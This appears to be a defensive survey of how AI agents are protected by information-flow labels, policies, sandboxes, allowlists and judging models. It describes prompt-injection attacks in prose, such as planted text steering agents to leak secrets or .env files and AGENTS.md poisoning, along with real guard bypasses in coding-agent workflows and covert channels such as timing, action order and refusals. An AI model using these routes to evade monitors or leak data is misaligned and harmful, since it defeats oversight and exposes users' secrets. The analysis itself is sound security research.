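CaMeL's developers have called a formal treatment a crucial direction for future work. Garby and colleagues found two gaps in CaMeL, which lacked such a treatment. The first is the skipped assignment described above. The second is outside CaMeL's interpreter, in the ordinary Python code that starts another attempt when a program fails. That code passes no label from the failed attempt to the next.

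Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt may reveal one bit. Guarantees that ignore termination usually allow a leak of one bit per run, but the retry loop can test something different about the secret on each attempt, eventually revealing all of it. To limit this leak, CaMeL censors the error messages it passes to the next attempt, but this gives no formal guarantee.

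Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL treats an untrusted value as trusted once a program inserts it into a text template. This mistake affects integrity, because an attacker's address could pass as a trusted recipient if the program built the recipient field from a template.

Their own agent avoids the retry problem by testing its program on invented data first. The planning model writes the program and corrects it until it works, and the agent then runs it on the real data. Failures during testing can't depend on real secrets, and retrying can't send a real email twice. Testing misses some errors, including violations of the information-flow rules, which appear only in the real run.

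It is unclear whether CaMeL's stricter tracking mode closes either gap, since Garby and colleagues report no test of it on these programs and no reply from CaMeL's developers. To stop the leak through the skipped assignment, a stricter mode would have to label variables in branches that don't run, or stop the program when it changes a public variable inside a secret condition. Adding more labels to assignments that run would not be enough. Closing the retry gap requires a change outside the interpreter.

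The gaps are more serious if an attacker can influence the program. A well-behaved planning model is unlikely to write the `tmp` and `rich` program by accident, and in CaMeL it writes its first program before it can read any emails. An attacker would have to influence the program some other way, such as through text the user pasted into the request or details left in an error message after censoring.

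### Choices, endings and delays

An agent that chooses among n visible actions can reveal up to log₂ n bits with each choice. The order of its actions can also reveal information. An agent can send five different messages in 120 orders, so the order alone can reveal up to 6.9 bits, even if the user dictated every word. FIDES leaves both channels open because explicit secrecy covers only the data that the calls copy.

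Termination leaks more when the observer can see steps the agent takes along the way than when the observer learns only whether the run finished. For example, a program might post 0000, 0001, 0002 and so on to a public page and get stuck when it reaches a secret code. The last number on the page then reveals the code in a single run. Askarov, Hunt, Sabelfeld and Sands analysed programs like this in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (2008).

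The LLMbda theorem compares final outcomes, so it doesn't cover posts from a run that gets stuck. But a real agent's posts are public as soon as the tool runs. To limit the leak to one bit per run, a developer would have to hold back all visible effects until the run finishes, which rules out tasks where the agent must wait for a reply.

None of these guarantees cover timing. If an agent reads a long appendix only when a memo mentions a merger, the extra reading delays its next web request, and the website's owner can measure the delay. Costa and colleagues also exclude the length of network packets, which can reveal the size of an encrypted message. A monitor could hide small delays by releasing actions at fixed intervals, but every task would then take longer.

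All of these channels matter more if the model itself is trying to pass information out.

### What an agent learns from a refusal

A refusal can itself reveal secret information to the agent. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) describes an attack in which planted text instructs an agent to read `/etc/shadow`, the file where Linux systems keep hashed passwords. The monitor blocks the call, but if it answers "permission denied" for a protected file and "file not found" for a missing one, the reply reveals that the file exists, and the agent can email that fact to the attacker. The failed call returned no data, so an ordinary taint tracker has no label to carry forward.

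Chinaei's defence, the Agentic Reference Monitor, keeps a graph of tool calls and the data that passed between them. It also records each refused call, links it to the next call the agent makes, and refuses that call too. The link depends only on timing, because the monitor can't detect whether the refusal influenced the model.

Chinaei acknowledges that this rule can block a harmless call that happens to follow a refusal, and can miss a leak that passes through several later steps. The published algorithm seems to have a worse problem, because it records the second refusal like the first and links it to the third call. One refusal would therefore block everything the agent tried afterwards.

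In Chinaei's test, the monitor stopped the email about the password file and two other attacks that a simple comparison system missed. He built all three scenarios by hand and ran them without a language model, so they show that the rule works as designed but not how often it would interrupt real tasks. The test also contains less of a leak than it seems to, because the monitor refuses `/etc/shadow` whether or not the file exists. The path is on a fixed list, so an agent that reports "shadow file exists" after the refusal is guessing.

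A refusal leaks a secret only if the secret affects it. Developers can therefore prevent much of this leakage by returning the same answer for forbidden and missing files. Where the answer has to depend on confidential facts, the software can give the refusal the same label as those facts, as it would for any other tool result.

Labels themselves can be confidential. If a company marks a folder "secret" only while it is negotiating a merger, a refusal to share the folder reveals the negotiations. LLMbda programs can test whether a value's label is at or below a level the program specifies, but the test doesn't reveal the label. The result's own label includes the specified level.

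Chinaei argues that FIDES would miss the attack on the password file, but this is doubtful for the published version, which ends the run at the first refusal. If the agent continued after reading the planted text into its conversation, the context would already be untrusted, so the integrity policy would refuse the email. The attack is more plausible against an agent that continues after refusals and checks only confidentiality, or one that takes its instructions from a trusted source.

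An attacker can also combine many refusals. Chinaei describes an attack that probes one file or service after another and reports the pattern of answers. Each answer reveals little by itself, but twenty independent yes-or-no answers can distinguish more than a million possible configurations.

### How quickly single bits add up

A four-digit code has 10,000 possible values, so it contains log₂ 10,000 ≈ 13.3 bits. If each run reveals the answer to one yes-or-no question, the first run might test whether the code is below 5,000, and each later run would halve the remaining range. Thirteen answers can distinguish only 2¹³ = 8,192 codes, but 14 can distinguish 16,384, so 14 runs are enough to find any code.

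Fewer runs are enough if each one has more visible outcomes:

| What an observer can see in each run | Possible outcomes | Bits per run | Runs needed for the code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whether the monitor refused | 2 | 1 | 14 |
| Which of four delays occurred | 4 | 2 | 7 |
| Which of eight actions the agent took | 8 | 3 | 5 |
| The order of five messages | 120 | 6.9 | 2 |

These figures assume that the attacker controls the question each time and that every answer is reliable. Random variation in the model's behaviour would increase the number of runs needed. A leak that is tolerable once may be unacceptable in a loop, because one bit about a four-digit code still leaves 5,000 possibilities, while 14 such leaks are enough to identify the code.

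Limits on retries therefore belong in the security policy, alongside the rules about labels. With at most three yes-or-no answers, an attacker can narrow 10,000 equally likely codes to about 1,250. This raises the chance of guessing the code from 1 in 10,000 to 1 in 1,250, which may be acceptable if the account locks after a few wrong guesses. The limit has to cover all runs combined for each secret, because an attacker who gets three answers per run could otherwise find the code in five runs.

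## Where do labels and policies come from, and what if they are wrong?

The proofs about FIDES and the LLMbda calculus assume that someone has already supplied labels and a policy. The monitor enforces these but cannot check whether they are right. If a stranger's text is labeled "trusted", the monitor will let it influence a payment. Zhou and Zhang list accurate labels among the assumptions on which several information-flow systems for agents depend.

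### Adding labels to existing software

In June 2026, Microsoft described prototypes that add labels to agent software already in use. Many agents use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools on separate servers. The prototypes put the labels in the metadata field of MCP messages, so software that doesn't support labels still works.

A label can cover a whole message or one part of it. In Microsoft's example, a call posts a message to a channel in Teams, its workplace chat program. The call as a whole is labeled untrusted and public, but the text of the message is labeled trusted and readable by only two people. Servers can also publish a policy for each tool, and the agent's software evaluates that policy before calling the tool.

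The prototypes cover different parts of the system:

- GitHub's MCP server can attach a label to the results of its tools.
- GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal, has an experimental setting that keeps a context label and checks it before certain calls. In June it covered only some of the GitHub server's tools and no other servers.
- A gateway adds labels for servers that don't supply them. For each tool, a developer describes the format of its results, writes a function to label them, and writes or picks a policy.
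- Microsoft Agent Framework, a library for building agents, has an experimental module based on FIDES, with variables and a quarantined model.

According to Microsoft's documentation, the Agent Framework module has only three confidentiality levels: public, private and user identity. For each tool that sends data out, the developer sets the highest level it may send. These levels are too coarse for the earlier example of Alex's inbox. If Priya's and Marco's emails are both labeled "private" and the mail tool may send private data, the module would let the agent send Marco the sales figures. Catching that leak requires a list of who may read the data.

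### The policy for posting to a Teams channel

Microsoft's sample policy for Teams does use lists of readers. Suppose Ana and Ben are allowed to read a piece of text, and an agent tries to post it to a channel.

| Context label | Channel members | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| trusted | Ana, Ben, Cleo | allow |
| untrusted | Ana, Ben | allow |
| untrusted | Ana, Ben, Cleo | ask the user, with a warning that Cleo would gain access |

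The policy looks up the channel's members at the time of the call, so it includes anyone who joined that morning. It blocks the call outright only if it can't complete the comparison, for example because the member list is missing.

Posting the text where Cleo can read it is a declassification. The policy is meant to provide robust declassification, which means that an attacker cannot trigger the release. Suppose an attacker rewrites all the untrusted data the agent can reach. If the context is trusted, none of that data has entered the conversation, so the model receives the same input as before and the attacker has not influenced its request. If some of the data has entered, the context is untrusted and the policy no longer releases anything automatically. The attacker can still cause the agent to ask the user, whose answer is then the only protection.

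This argument assumes that the context label covers everything that shaped the message, which isn't always true of an agent that uses variables. Suppose a quarantined model summarises a stranger's email together with a confidential forecast, and a sentence planted in the email makes it copy the forecast into the summary. The planning model has read neither the email nor the forecast, so its context is still trusted. If it posts the summary by variable name, the sample policy allows the post without checking who is in the channel. The attacker has then chosen what the post reveals, though not when or where it is posted.

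The strict integrity policy from Costa and colleagues would block this post because the summary is untrusted. A developer could fix the Teams policy by making it skip the reader comparison only when both the context and the text are trusted.

### Using a repository's visibility as a label

GitHub's server labels text without information about who first wrote each sentence, so it bases the label largely on whether the repository is public. Microsoft reports that the server labels files and issues from public repositories "untrusted, public" and those from private repositories "trusted, private".

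The labels are meant to counter the GitHub attack described earlier, which Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner demonstrated in May 2025. According to *GitHub MCP Exploited* (Willison, 2025), they planted an issue in which they praised a project, complained that its author wasn't well known enough, and told the agent to read the introductory files in the author's other repositories.

GitHub's code differs from Microsoft's description. pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026) documents version 1.0.5, from May 2026, which labels files from private repositories as trusted because only collaborators can add changes. It labels all issues as untrusted, even in private repositories. A planted issue in a private repository could therefore steer an agent without raising its context label under Microsoft's description, but not under GitHub's code. The latest release of GitHub's software no longer contains the *ifc*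 package, so the rules may have changed.

Either version can treat text as trusted when it shouldn't. A private repository may contain code from another company, error logs with text that customers typed, or a bug report that an employee copied from an email. A collaborator who agreed to store this text didn't necessarily agree to let an agent follow instructions in it.

The rule can also be too strict. It marks a public project's own instructions as untrusted even if its maintainers wrote every word. GitHub's lockdown mode makes a finer distinction by restricting content that untrusted contributors post in public repositories (GitHub, 2025). But the account that posts a text doesn't always show who wrote it, since a trusted contributor can paste in a stranger's words.

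Confidentiality labels have similar problems. GitHub's code marks restricted data with the word "private", and the agent's software has to look up who can actually read the data when it is about to send it elsewhere. A monitor that compared only the word would let text from one private repository into another with different collaborators. If the text is going to Teams, someone also has to match GitHub accounts to Teams accounts.

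For a search across several repositories, the result is private if any matching repository is private. An empty result counts as public, on the grounds that it reveals no repository data. But if an agent searches a company's private repositories for a customer's name and finds nothing, the empty result reveals that no repository it searched mentions that customer.

### What one wrong label can do

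Suppose a company's support staff save customers' bug reports as files in a private repository, which also holds a confidential price list. One customer's report contains a hidden instruction to post the price list to a Teams channel that the company shares with its resellers. A developer asks an agent connected to both GitHub and Teams to investigate the bug.

| Step | With GitHub's label for private files | With a correct label |
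|---|---|---|
| The agent reads the bug report | context is trusted | context is untrusted |
| The model obeys the instruction and reads the price list | context is trusted and private | context is untrusted and private |
| The model requests a post to the resellers' channel | the Teams policy allows it | the policy finds that resellers may not read the list, and asks the developer |

The price list had the correct confidentiality label throughout, but the Teams policy ignored it because the context was wrongly labeled as trusted. One wrong integrity label therefore disabled both protections. A policy that always compared the list's permitted readers with the channel's members would have caught the leak despite the error. This is a reason to require both the integrity and confidentiality checks for the most sensitive data, even though users will then have to confirm some releases they intended.

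### Forgotten labels and dishonest tools

A developer may also forget to label a tool's results. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) said that the Agent Framework module treats such a tool as trusted and public, and invited comments on a stricter default. The module's documentation from June gives the default as untrusted and public.

With the new default, a mistake leads to a refusal in the integrity check but not in the confidentiality check, although Microsoft describes the default as failing closed. In the documentation's main example, a planted instruction makes an agent read a project's `.env` file, which often contains passwords, and try to post it as a public comment. The monitor blocks the comment because the developer labelled the file's contents "private". Without that label, the confidentiality check would treat the contents as public and let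 the agent post them.

The documentation also gives another rule for tools that declare nothing, which is that the result takes the combined label of the tool's inputs. Under this rule, if an agent requested a web search from a trusted context, the search results would be labelled trusted. Developers therefore need to test which rule their installed version applies.

A developer can also declare one integrity label for everything a tool returns, and this label replaces the combined label of the inputs. That makes sense for a tool that fetches outside data. But if a developer declares a translation tool "trusted", its translation of an untrusted email is labeled trusted too. The documentation gives an internal database as an example of a trusted source, but many internal databases contain text that customers typed, such as names, addresses and complaints.

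To save developers from labelling every tool by hand, Microsoft suggests using the descriptions that MCP servers already provide. A server can describe a tool as read-only, as destructive, or as open-world, which means that it deals with outside parties. The suggested rules are:

| The server's description of the tool | Policy |
|---|---|
| Read-only, not open-world | always allow |
| Read-only, open-world | allow only if all arguments are public |
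| Destructive | ask the user |

The software can also infer labels for results. It can treat the output of open-world tools as untrusted and the output of tools that require a login as private.

These rules are only as reliable as the tool descriptions. Suppose the maker of a spelling checker describes it as read-only and not open-world, but the tool sends the maker every text it checks. The monitor would always allow the call, so the maker would receive any confidential draft the agent checked. Costa and colleagues exclude this case from their threat model by assuming that tool descriptions are trustworthy.

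Zhou and Zhang describe a partial remedy called ETDI, in which providers sign each version of a tool's description. A signature can show who wrote the description and whether anyone has altered it since, but not whether the description is true.

### Policies that a model writes for each task

Even with accurate labels, someone has to decide which actions a task requires. Sending email is part of answering urgent messages but not of sorting an inbox. Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025), in *Contextual Agent Security*, propose having a language model write a new policy for each request. Their system, Conseca, works in four steps:

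1. A policy model receives the user's request, descriptions of the tools, and context that the developer has chosen to trust, such as the user's name and a list of file names. It doesn't see the contents of emails or files.
2. It writes a rule for each tool, saying whether the agent may use it and with which arguments, and gives a reason that a person can read.
3. The agent's own model, which may read anything, proposes actions.
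4. Ordinary software compares each action with the rules. If it refuses one, it returns the reason so that the agent can try something else.

A planted email can't change the policy, because the policy model never receives it. In one test, Tsai and Bagdasarian added an email with instructions to forward all messages about urgent security vulnerabilities. Conseca blocked all forwarding unless the user had asked the agent to perform the tasks in urgent emails.

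The policy can still be wrong. In a published example, Alice asks the agent to answer urgent work emails. The stated reason for the rule is that the recipient must be on a list of users from work, but the rule only checks whether the address contains "@work.com". It would also accept `eve@work.com.example.net`, which belongs to whoever controls example.net. The software would enforce this faulty rule consistently. Tsai and Bagdasarian rely on experts, perhaps automated ones, to check that rules match their stated reasons.

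Conseca also depends on which context the developer chooses to trust. The prototype trusts file names, but if an agent saves attachments under their original names, an outsider can use those names to insert text into the policy model's input. Giving that model less context makes it safer but less able to predict what a task will require. For example, it can't write a precise policy for "carry out the tasks in my manager's email" without reading the email.

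*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Conseca implicitly assumes that its policy generator is safe, which undermines its guarantees. Tsai and Bagdasarian state this dependence explicitly. They promise only that no tool call will violate the policy, and they say the policy is only as good as the model's understanding of the user, social norms and the task.

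### Policies that change during a task

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) lets the policy change as the agent learns more. Each rule allows or forbids a tool call when the call's arguments meet certain conditions. Rules that forbid take priority, and the software blocks any call that no rule allows.

In their main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. The list says to summarise recent emails and post the summary to the user's account on Slack, a chat service. One of those emails contains a planted instruction to forward the inbox to an outsider. A language model writes the first policy from the request and then proposes changes:

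| What the agent has just read | Proposed change | Type of change |
|---|---|---|
| The to-do list | also allow reading recent emails, looking up the user's Slack name and sending Slack messages | expansion |
| The user's Slack name, `alice` | allow Slack messages only to `alice` | narrowing |
| Recent emails, including the planted one | also allow emails to the outsider, if the attack fools the model | expansion |

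Progent applies a narrowing automatically but requires approval for an expansion. To tell them apart, it uses an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true at once. Let A(P) be the set of tool calls that policy P allows. A change from P to P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

and an expansion otherwise. For each tool, the solver looks for arguments that P′ would allow and P would not. If the old rule allows payments up to $100 and the new one allows payments up to $200, a payment of $150 is such a case, so the change is an expansion. If the new limit is $50, no such payment exists. A change that removes one permission and adds another is still an expansion.

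Shi and colleagues prove that the set of permitted calls can only shrink between approvals, even if an attacker controls what the policy model reads. This property, which they call monotonic confinement, doesn't guarantee that the first policy was right. They assume that the user's request is harmless and expect the model to turn it into suitably narrow rules.

Progent's security also depends on how expansions are approved. A developer can have the software approve all of them, refuse all of them, follow a rule for each tool or ask a person. In the example, both expansions come from text in an email, and the solver can't distinguish Alice's legitimate list from the planted instruction. An approver needs to know who wrote each text and whether the user meant to follow it. An integrity label can help identify who wrote it. Approving the to-do list's expansion amounts to endorsing Alice's email.

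A narrowing can also be harmful. Suppose an attacker alters the result of the Slack lookup so that it gives the user's name as `eve`. If the policy model then changes "messages to anyone" to "messages only to `eve`", Progent applies the change without approval because it is a narrowing. The agent can now send the summary to Eve but not to the user. Monotonic confinement still holds, because the earlier policy already allowed messages to Eve.

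### Policies that labels express badly

Some policies limit the purpose for which people may use data. A clinic might be allowed to use a patient's phone number for appointment reminders but not for advertising. Both kinds of message go to the patient through the same tool, and the number has the same permitted readers in each case. The clinic could add "reminders only" to the label, but the monitor would then need to determine from a message's content whether it was a reminder or an advertisement.

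Labels also don't record whether data is accurate or up to date. An address book can be fully trusted and still contain an old address. Zhou and Zhang point out that a change of contact details or a withdrawn approval can make a message improper after the agent has queued it. To catch this, the monitor has to recheck the facts when the message goes out.

Combining public facts can produce sensitive information. One public page might list a company's night guards, and another might show which of them are on holiday. A text that combines the two could reveal when a building is unguarded, but it would still be labelled public, because the join of two public labels is public. Tsai and Bagdasarian give a related example about quantity, in which sending one email is harmless but flooding an inbox is not. Costa and colleagues note that a monitor could keep a history of the agent's actions and check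 it alongside the labels, which would let it limit the number of emails.

A single "trusted" label also does not distinguish supplying a fact from granting permission. In Zhou and Zhang's example, a company directory may supply a recipient's address but has no authority to approve sending that person more data. A policy with separate rules for each argument can accept the address from the directory while requiring the user to decide whether to send the message.

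The user's intent is the hardest thing to express in a policy. If she asks an agent to delete unimportant files and it deletes her tax records, an information-flow policy would allow the deletion, because the request was trusted, no secret leaked, and no outsider influenced the choice. A policy from Conseca or Progent might limit deletions to a temporary folder, but the model that writes the policy also has to guess which files she considers unimportant.

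## How do permission guards fail?

Labels are still uncommon in everyday agents. According to *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026), existing systems usually control agents by restricting their tools, arguments, resources or account permissions. Such a check is a permission guard. It allows an action, refuses it or refers it to a person, without tracking where the data in it came from. Four kinds are common:

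- An approval prompt shows the user a proposed action and waits for a yes or no.
- An allowlist names the commands an agent may run, or the destinations it may contact, without asking. Progent's rules are a more detailed version.
- A sandbox runs the agent's commands in a closed environment, where the operating system blocks access to protected files and often to the network.
- A judging model is a separate language model that reads each proposed action and decides whether to allow it.

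These guards fail for several different reasons, and tracking data flow would prevent only some of the failures.

### The rule checks the wrong part of the action

Suppose a coding agent has to upload a status report to an approved server, and someone has planted an instruction in a project file to include a secret key. A rule that checks only the destination will allow the upload even if it contains the key. Singh and Srinivasa (2026), in *Where Agent Defenses Fail*, tested this case and others like it. Their pilot had 110 runs, covering seven attack tasks and four harmless ones, and a larger set had 300 runs, covering 18 attack tasks and 12 harmless ones. Each task ran twice in each of five setups. They measured harm by what reached the servers and which protected files changed, not by what the guards logged.

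The setups combine three components. An allowlist checks the path, destination or command in each proposed call. A sandbox makes protected files read-only and has no network connection. A mediator outside the sandbox sends any request the allowlist has approved, so the agent can still upload its report.

| Setup | Pilot: attack runs with harm | Pilot: harmless runs completed | Larger set: attack runs with harm | Larger set: harmless runs completed |
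|---|---|---|---|---|
| No guard | 7 of 14 | 8 of 8 | 12 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| Allowlist | 2 of 14 | 8 of 8 | 6 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| Sandbox | 0 of 14 | 6 of 8 | 0 of 36 | 12 of 24 |
| Allowlist, sandbox and mediator | 2 of 14 | 8 of 8 | 4 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| The same, with a check for secret lines | 0 of 14 | 8 of 8 | 2 of 36 | 24 of 24 |

With the sandbox alone, no attack run caused observable harm, but every harmless run that needed the network failed. In the pilot, these were two runs of a single upload task. Adding the mediator allowed all the uploads to succeed, but it also delivered secrets in two pilot runs and four runs of the larger set, because the allowlist had approved the server and no component checked the contents.

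In the last setup, the mediator refused any request that contained a complete line from a secret file. One attack in the larger set got past this check in both runs by sending the key without the variable name in front of it. In a separate test, the check also missed a secret the agent had encoded.

These numbers don't measure how often such leaks happen in practice. Singh and Srinivasa used one open-weight model on a local machine, wrote the tasks themselves and did not adapt the attacks to the defences. Half of the pilot's attack runs did no harm even without a guard, so a zero in the table doesn't mean that a guard stopped 14 attacks. Singh and Srinivasa also built the mediator, and a commercial one might check what it sends. But their working example shows that a component added to restore useful work can undo another component's protection.

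A mediator can check the contents if the developer knows exactly what the agent should send. In a follow-up, Singh and Srinivasa had the mediator accept only four exact messages. It refused both attacks, but also both harmless uploads, because the agent had written a line break as a backslash and the letter n. After each refusal, the agent claimed to have published the message. A more tolerant version accepted both harmless uploads and still refused both attacks. Neither version would work for a summary whose wording nobody can predict.

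Tracking data flow would have stopped these leaks, because the context label would have kept the key's restriction even if the model shortened or encoded the key. Singh and Srinivasa tested a rule that works much like a context label. Once the agent had read a registered secret file, the rule blocked all the agent's web requests and shell commands. No secret leaked in the six attack runs with this rule, but the rule also blocked harmless uploads. Keeping the secret in a variable, as FIDES can do, would avoid some of those blocks.

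Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, had a similar fault. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) explains that its web-fetching tool had pre-approved all of Hugging Face, a site where anyone can publish AI models. The rule checked the site's name but not the page, so the agent could fetch an attacker's files without asking the user. The site counts each fetch as a download, so a hijacked agent could signal data to the attacker through its choice of files. INCIBE lists the severity as medium. Anthropic fixed the fault in version 2.1.163, and according to the GitLab Advisory Database, users with automatic updates received the fix before the advisory appeared.

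A context label would have covered this leak too, if the monitor treated the page's address as outgoing data. If the developer lists the fetching tool as read-only, the monitor will miss the leak, as the allowlist did.

### The guard and the computer interpret a command differently

The download-counter fault was the last of three that Elad Meged, a researcher at the security firm Novee, found in Claude Code's workflow for GitHub. The workflow runs the agent automatically on issues and proposed changes, which strangers can write. Witts (2026) reports in *Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex* that Meged attacked Anthropic's, Google's and OpenAI's own repositories with default settings, so the companies could not blame a user's configuration. He disclosed his findings on all three companies in late July 2026, and each has since made changes.

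Meged's first attack on Anthropic's workflow had to get past 23 checks for malicious commands. The checks treated one git option as harmless text, but git treated the same text as the name of a program to start, so an attacker could run any code.

Earlier faults in Claude Code had the same cause. The GitHub Advisory Database's *GHSA-mhg7-666j-cqg4* (2026) describes one in which an agent could write to forbidden files by chaining two commands that the validator did not analyse properly. In a 2025 case in the GitLab Advisory Database, the software compared only the beginning of a file path with the permitted folder's path, so it also permitted other folders whose names began the same way.

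A sandbox is stronger here because the operating system checks the file that a command reaches, however the command is written. When agents in Singh and Srinivasa's tests tried to change a protected file through an alias, the allowlist missed the attempt and the sandbox blocked it.

Labels would help with some of these faults. If a stranger's issue led the agent to run the git command, the command would be labelled "untrusted", and a strict integrity policy would block it however git interpreted the option. However, policies usually let an untrusted context run commands that only read data, so the monitor has to identify those commands. If it misclassified the git command as read-only, it would make the same error as Anthropic's checks. A monitor that misinterprets a path can also give a file's contents the wrong label.

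### Permitted steps combine into a forbidden flow

After the git attack, Anthropic removed the workflow's access to the command line. Meged then extracted secrets with commands that the software approved automatically because they only read data. Meged explained in Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* that such attacks publish a secret through two decisions that are each reasonable alone. The software approves a command because it looks safe, and it publishes the output because that is the default.

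Anthropic paid for each report and patched each fault. Meged said the patches were not careless, but he learned from each one where to look next. He recommends checking whether something is safe at the point where a later component uses it, because a judgment such as "this command only reads" may not hold there.

A label makes this possible because it stays with the data. The secret would still be restricted when the workflow tried to publish the output, so the monitor would block the attempt.

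Some combinations of actions go beyond the user's request without breaking any rule about labels. *Runtime Authorization Consistency Checking for MCP-based Agentic Workflows* (Zhang, Lee and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an assistant only to find free slots in her calendar. The assistant also has standing access to her email and chat. It searches her emails for context, infers a conflict and messages a colleague to reschedule. If the emails come from trusted colleagues and the recipient may read them, an information-flow monitor would not block the message.

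Zhang and colleagues built a guard called RAC for this problem. It starts with a trusted statement of what the task permits, passes that permission from each accepted step to the next, and blocks any call that exceeds it. They tested it on 1,248 workflows, 1,008 of which should be blocked. RAC missed none of those, while the best simpler guard, which combined fixed rules with a history of earlier calls, missed 509. Since the researchers also designed the test workflows, the perfect score mostly confirms that the rules work as intended. On selected plans written by a language model, RAC caught 92.8 per cent of the workflows it should have blocked, compared with 68.8 per cent for the best alternative.

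RAC depends on someone stating the task's limits correctly. It also blocks any step that draws on several earlier steps, which would rule out many ordinary reports.

### An effect takes a path the guard does not see

Google's case was the most severe of the three. The GitHub Advisory Database's *GHSA-wpqr-6v78-jr5g* (2026) rates it 10.0, the highest possible score, and describes two faults in Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent for the command line:

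- In a mode that approves actions without prompts, the program ignored detailed allowlists. An operator who had allowed one harmless command had in effect allowed every command.
- When the program ran with no person at the keyboard, it automatically trusted the folder it was working in and loaded settings from it. In a workflow that reviews strangers' code, a stranger could supply those settings and use them to run code.

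The advisory credits Meged and Dan Lisichkin of Pillar Security. According to Help Net Security, Meged used the configuration that Google's documentation recommended for untrusted input. Google now enforces the allowlist in that mode and requires the operator to mark a folder as trusted. It warned that these changes would break some existing workflows.

Witts describes another gap in Gemini CLI. Google had removed secrets from the environment of the commands the agent ran, but those commands could still read the secrets from the program that had started them.

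Tracking data flow would fail in the same way, because a mode that skips the allowlist could also skip the label check. Settings from a stranger's folder are a worse problem, because they take effect before the agent has read anything the monitor could label. The mediator in Singh and Srinivasa's study also created a path around a guard, because the sandbox restricted only what ran inside it. Monitoring files and network connections below the level of tool calls can cover some of these paths.

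### Something approved changes before use

An approval covers an action or file only as it was when someone checked it. In OpenAI's workflow for its coding agent, Codex, two runs shared a folder. During the first run, an attacker's text could make the agent write instructions into a file, AGENTS.md. The second run had more permissions and loaded that file as trusted instructions. Underhill (2026), in *Black Hat 2026*, reports that OpenAI responded by separating the stages in its own repository and documenting the file as an untrusted input. The researchers warned that other organisations with similar workflows might still be vulnerable.

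A user can create the same problem by approving a command that runs a script. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) points out that such a command can look routine while authorising whatever code the script contains. If the user also clicked "don't ask again", the approval covers any code that the agent or an outsider later puts in the script.

One remedy is to tie each approval to a specific effect. Zhou and Zhang describe a system called SUDP, in which the user approves a standard description of an operation. A separate program holds the passwords and carries out an operation only if it matches the description. ZTAC works out which object a call will affect before authorising it, then checks that the call reaches the same object when it runs. *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) tested several designs of this kind. With simulated approvers, each design completed all 97 harmless AgentDojo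 tasks, with an average of 0.75 prompts per task.

Labels would have stopped the Codex attack if they had stayed with the file. In the labelled loop from Costa and colleagues, AGENTS.md and the next run's context would both have been labelled untrusted. But if the software kept labels for only one run, the file would have reached the next run unlabelled. A file's label also won't reflect a change that someone makes outside the agent, unless the monitor recomputes the label each time the agent reads the file.

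### The judging model gets it wrong

A judging model can assess actions that no list covers, but it may read text that an attacker wrote to influence its decision. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a judging model that receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic withholds tool results because they may contain planted instructions, and the agent's explanations because a hijacked agent could use them to argue for its action. A separate check scans tool results and warns the agent about suspicious text.

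An attacker's words can still reach this judge if the agent copies them into the arguments of a call. Hiding the results also removes useful evidence. If an agent asks to cancel a job that the user never named, Anthropic's judge can't check whether the agent found the job's name in a query or made it up.

Anthropic tested the judge on three sets of actions:

| Test set | Size | Errors |
|---|---|---|
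| Ordinary actions by Anthropic employees' agents | 10,000 | blocked 0.4 per cent |
| Artificial attempts to send private data out | 1,000 | missed 5.7 per cent |
| Real actions that went beyond what an employee wanted | 52 | missed 17 per cent |

In most of the missed cases that Anthropic examined, the judge identified the danger but misjudged what the user had agreed to. For example, it treated "Clean up the PR" (a PR is a proposed code change) as permission to overwrite the project's history.

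In a later evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, none of 720 prompt injection attempts succeeded against Anthropic's newest models with auto mode on. But only 0.09 per cent succeeded against its latest models with no permission checks, so the result is better evidence of the models' resistance to injection than of the judge's effectiveness.

Judges can also fail when nobody is trying to mislead them. In another of Singh and Srinivasa's tests, a scanner passed some suspicious calls to a judging model. Of the model's 18 judgments, 12 produced an error. When the researchers replayed those 12, the model reached its output limit before answering. The software blocked these calls, which was safe but would have stopped harmless work too. Meanwhile, the agent sent out encoded secrets in calls that never reached the judge.

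Planted text can't make a monitor ignore a label, although designs that use a model to estimate labels, such as RTBAS, lose part of this advantage. An integrity label would also give Anthropic's judge some of the evidence it lacks, by recording whether an untrusted source could have influenced the job's name.

A judge is the better guard against actions that merely go too far. If a user asks an agent to tidy up some code branches and it tries to delete ones she needs, an information-flow monitor would allow the deletion, as it would for the tax records in the earlier example. Anthropic designed its judge to block such actions.

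### People approve out of habit

Anthropic's account of how it built auto mode reported that Claude Code users accepted 93 per cent of permission prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) puts the figure at 97 per cent. Most requests are harmless, so a high rate doesn't prove carelessness. But users rejected 39 per cent of the plans Claude presented for approval, so they do object when asked about the work as a whole.

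Anthropic also tested people's attention. A research vendor had 1,053 paid testers do coding work and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Of these testers, 143 (13.6 per cent) refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17 per cent early in a session to about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic's judging model blocked 89 per cent of the same commands. The company published these results to support a change to its product. The testers may also have been less careful than developers are with their own projects, because mistakes in the test environment had no consequences for them.

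Many users stop answering prompts. Anthropic says that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips permission checks. In an earlier Anthropic study, summarised in Resilient Cyber's *the human in the loop illusion*, new users approved everything automatically in about 20 per cent of sessions, and users with 750 sessions did so in more than 40 per cent. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) note in *From Delegation to Action Approval* that experienced users in that study also interrupted the agent more often. Some of them seem to have switched from approving each step to watching the work and stepping in.

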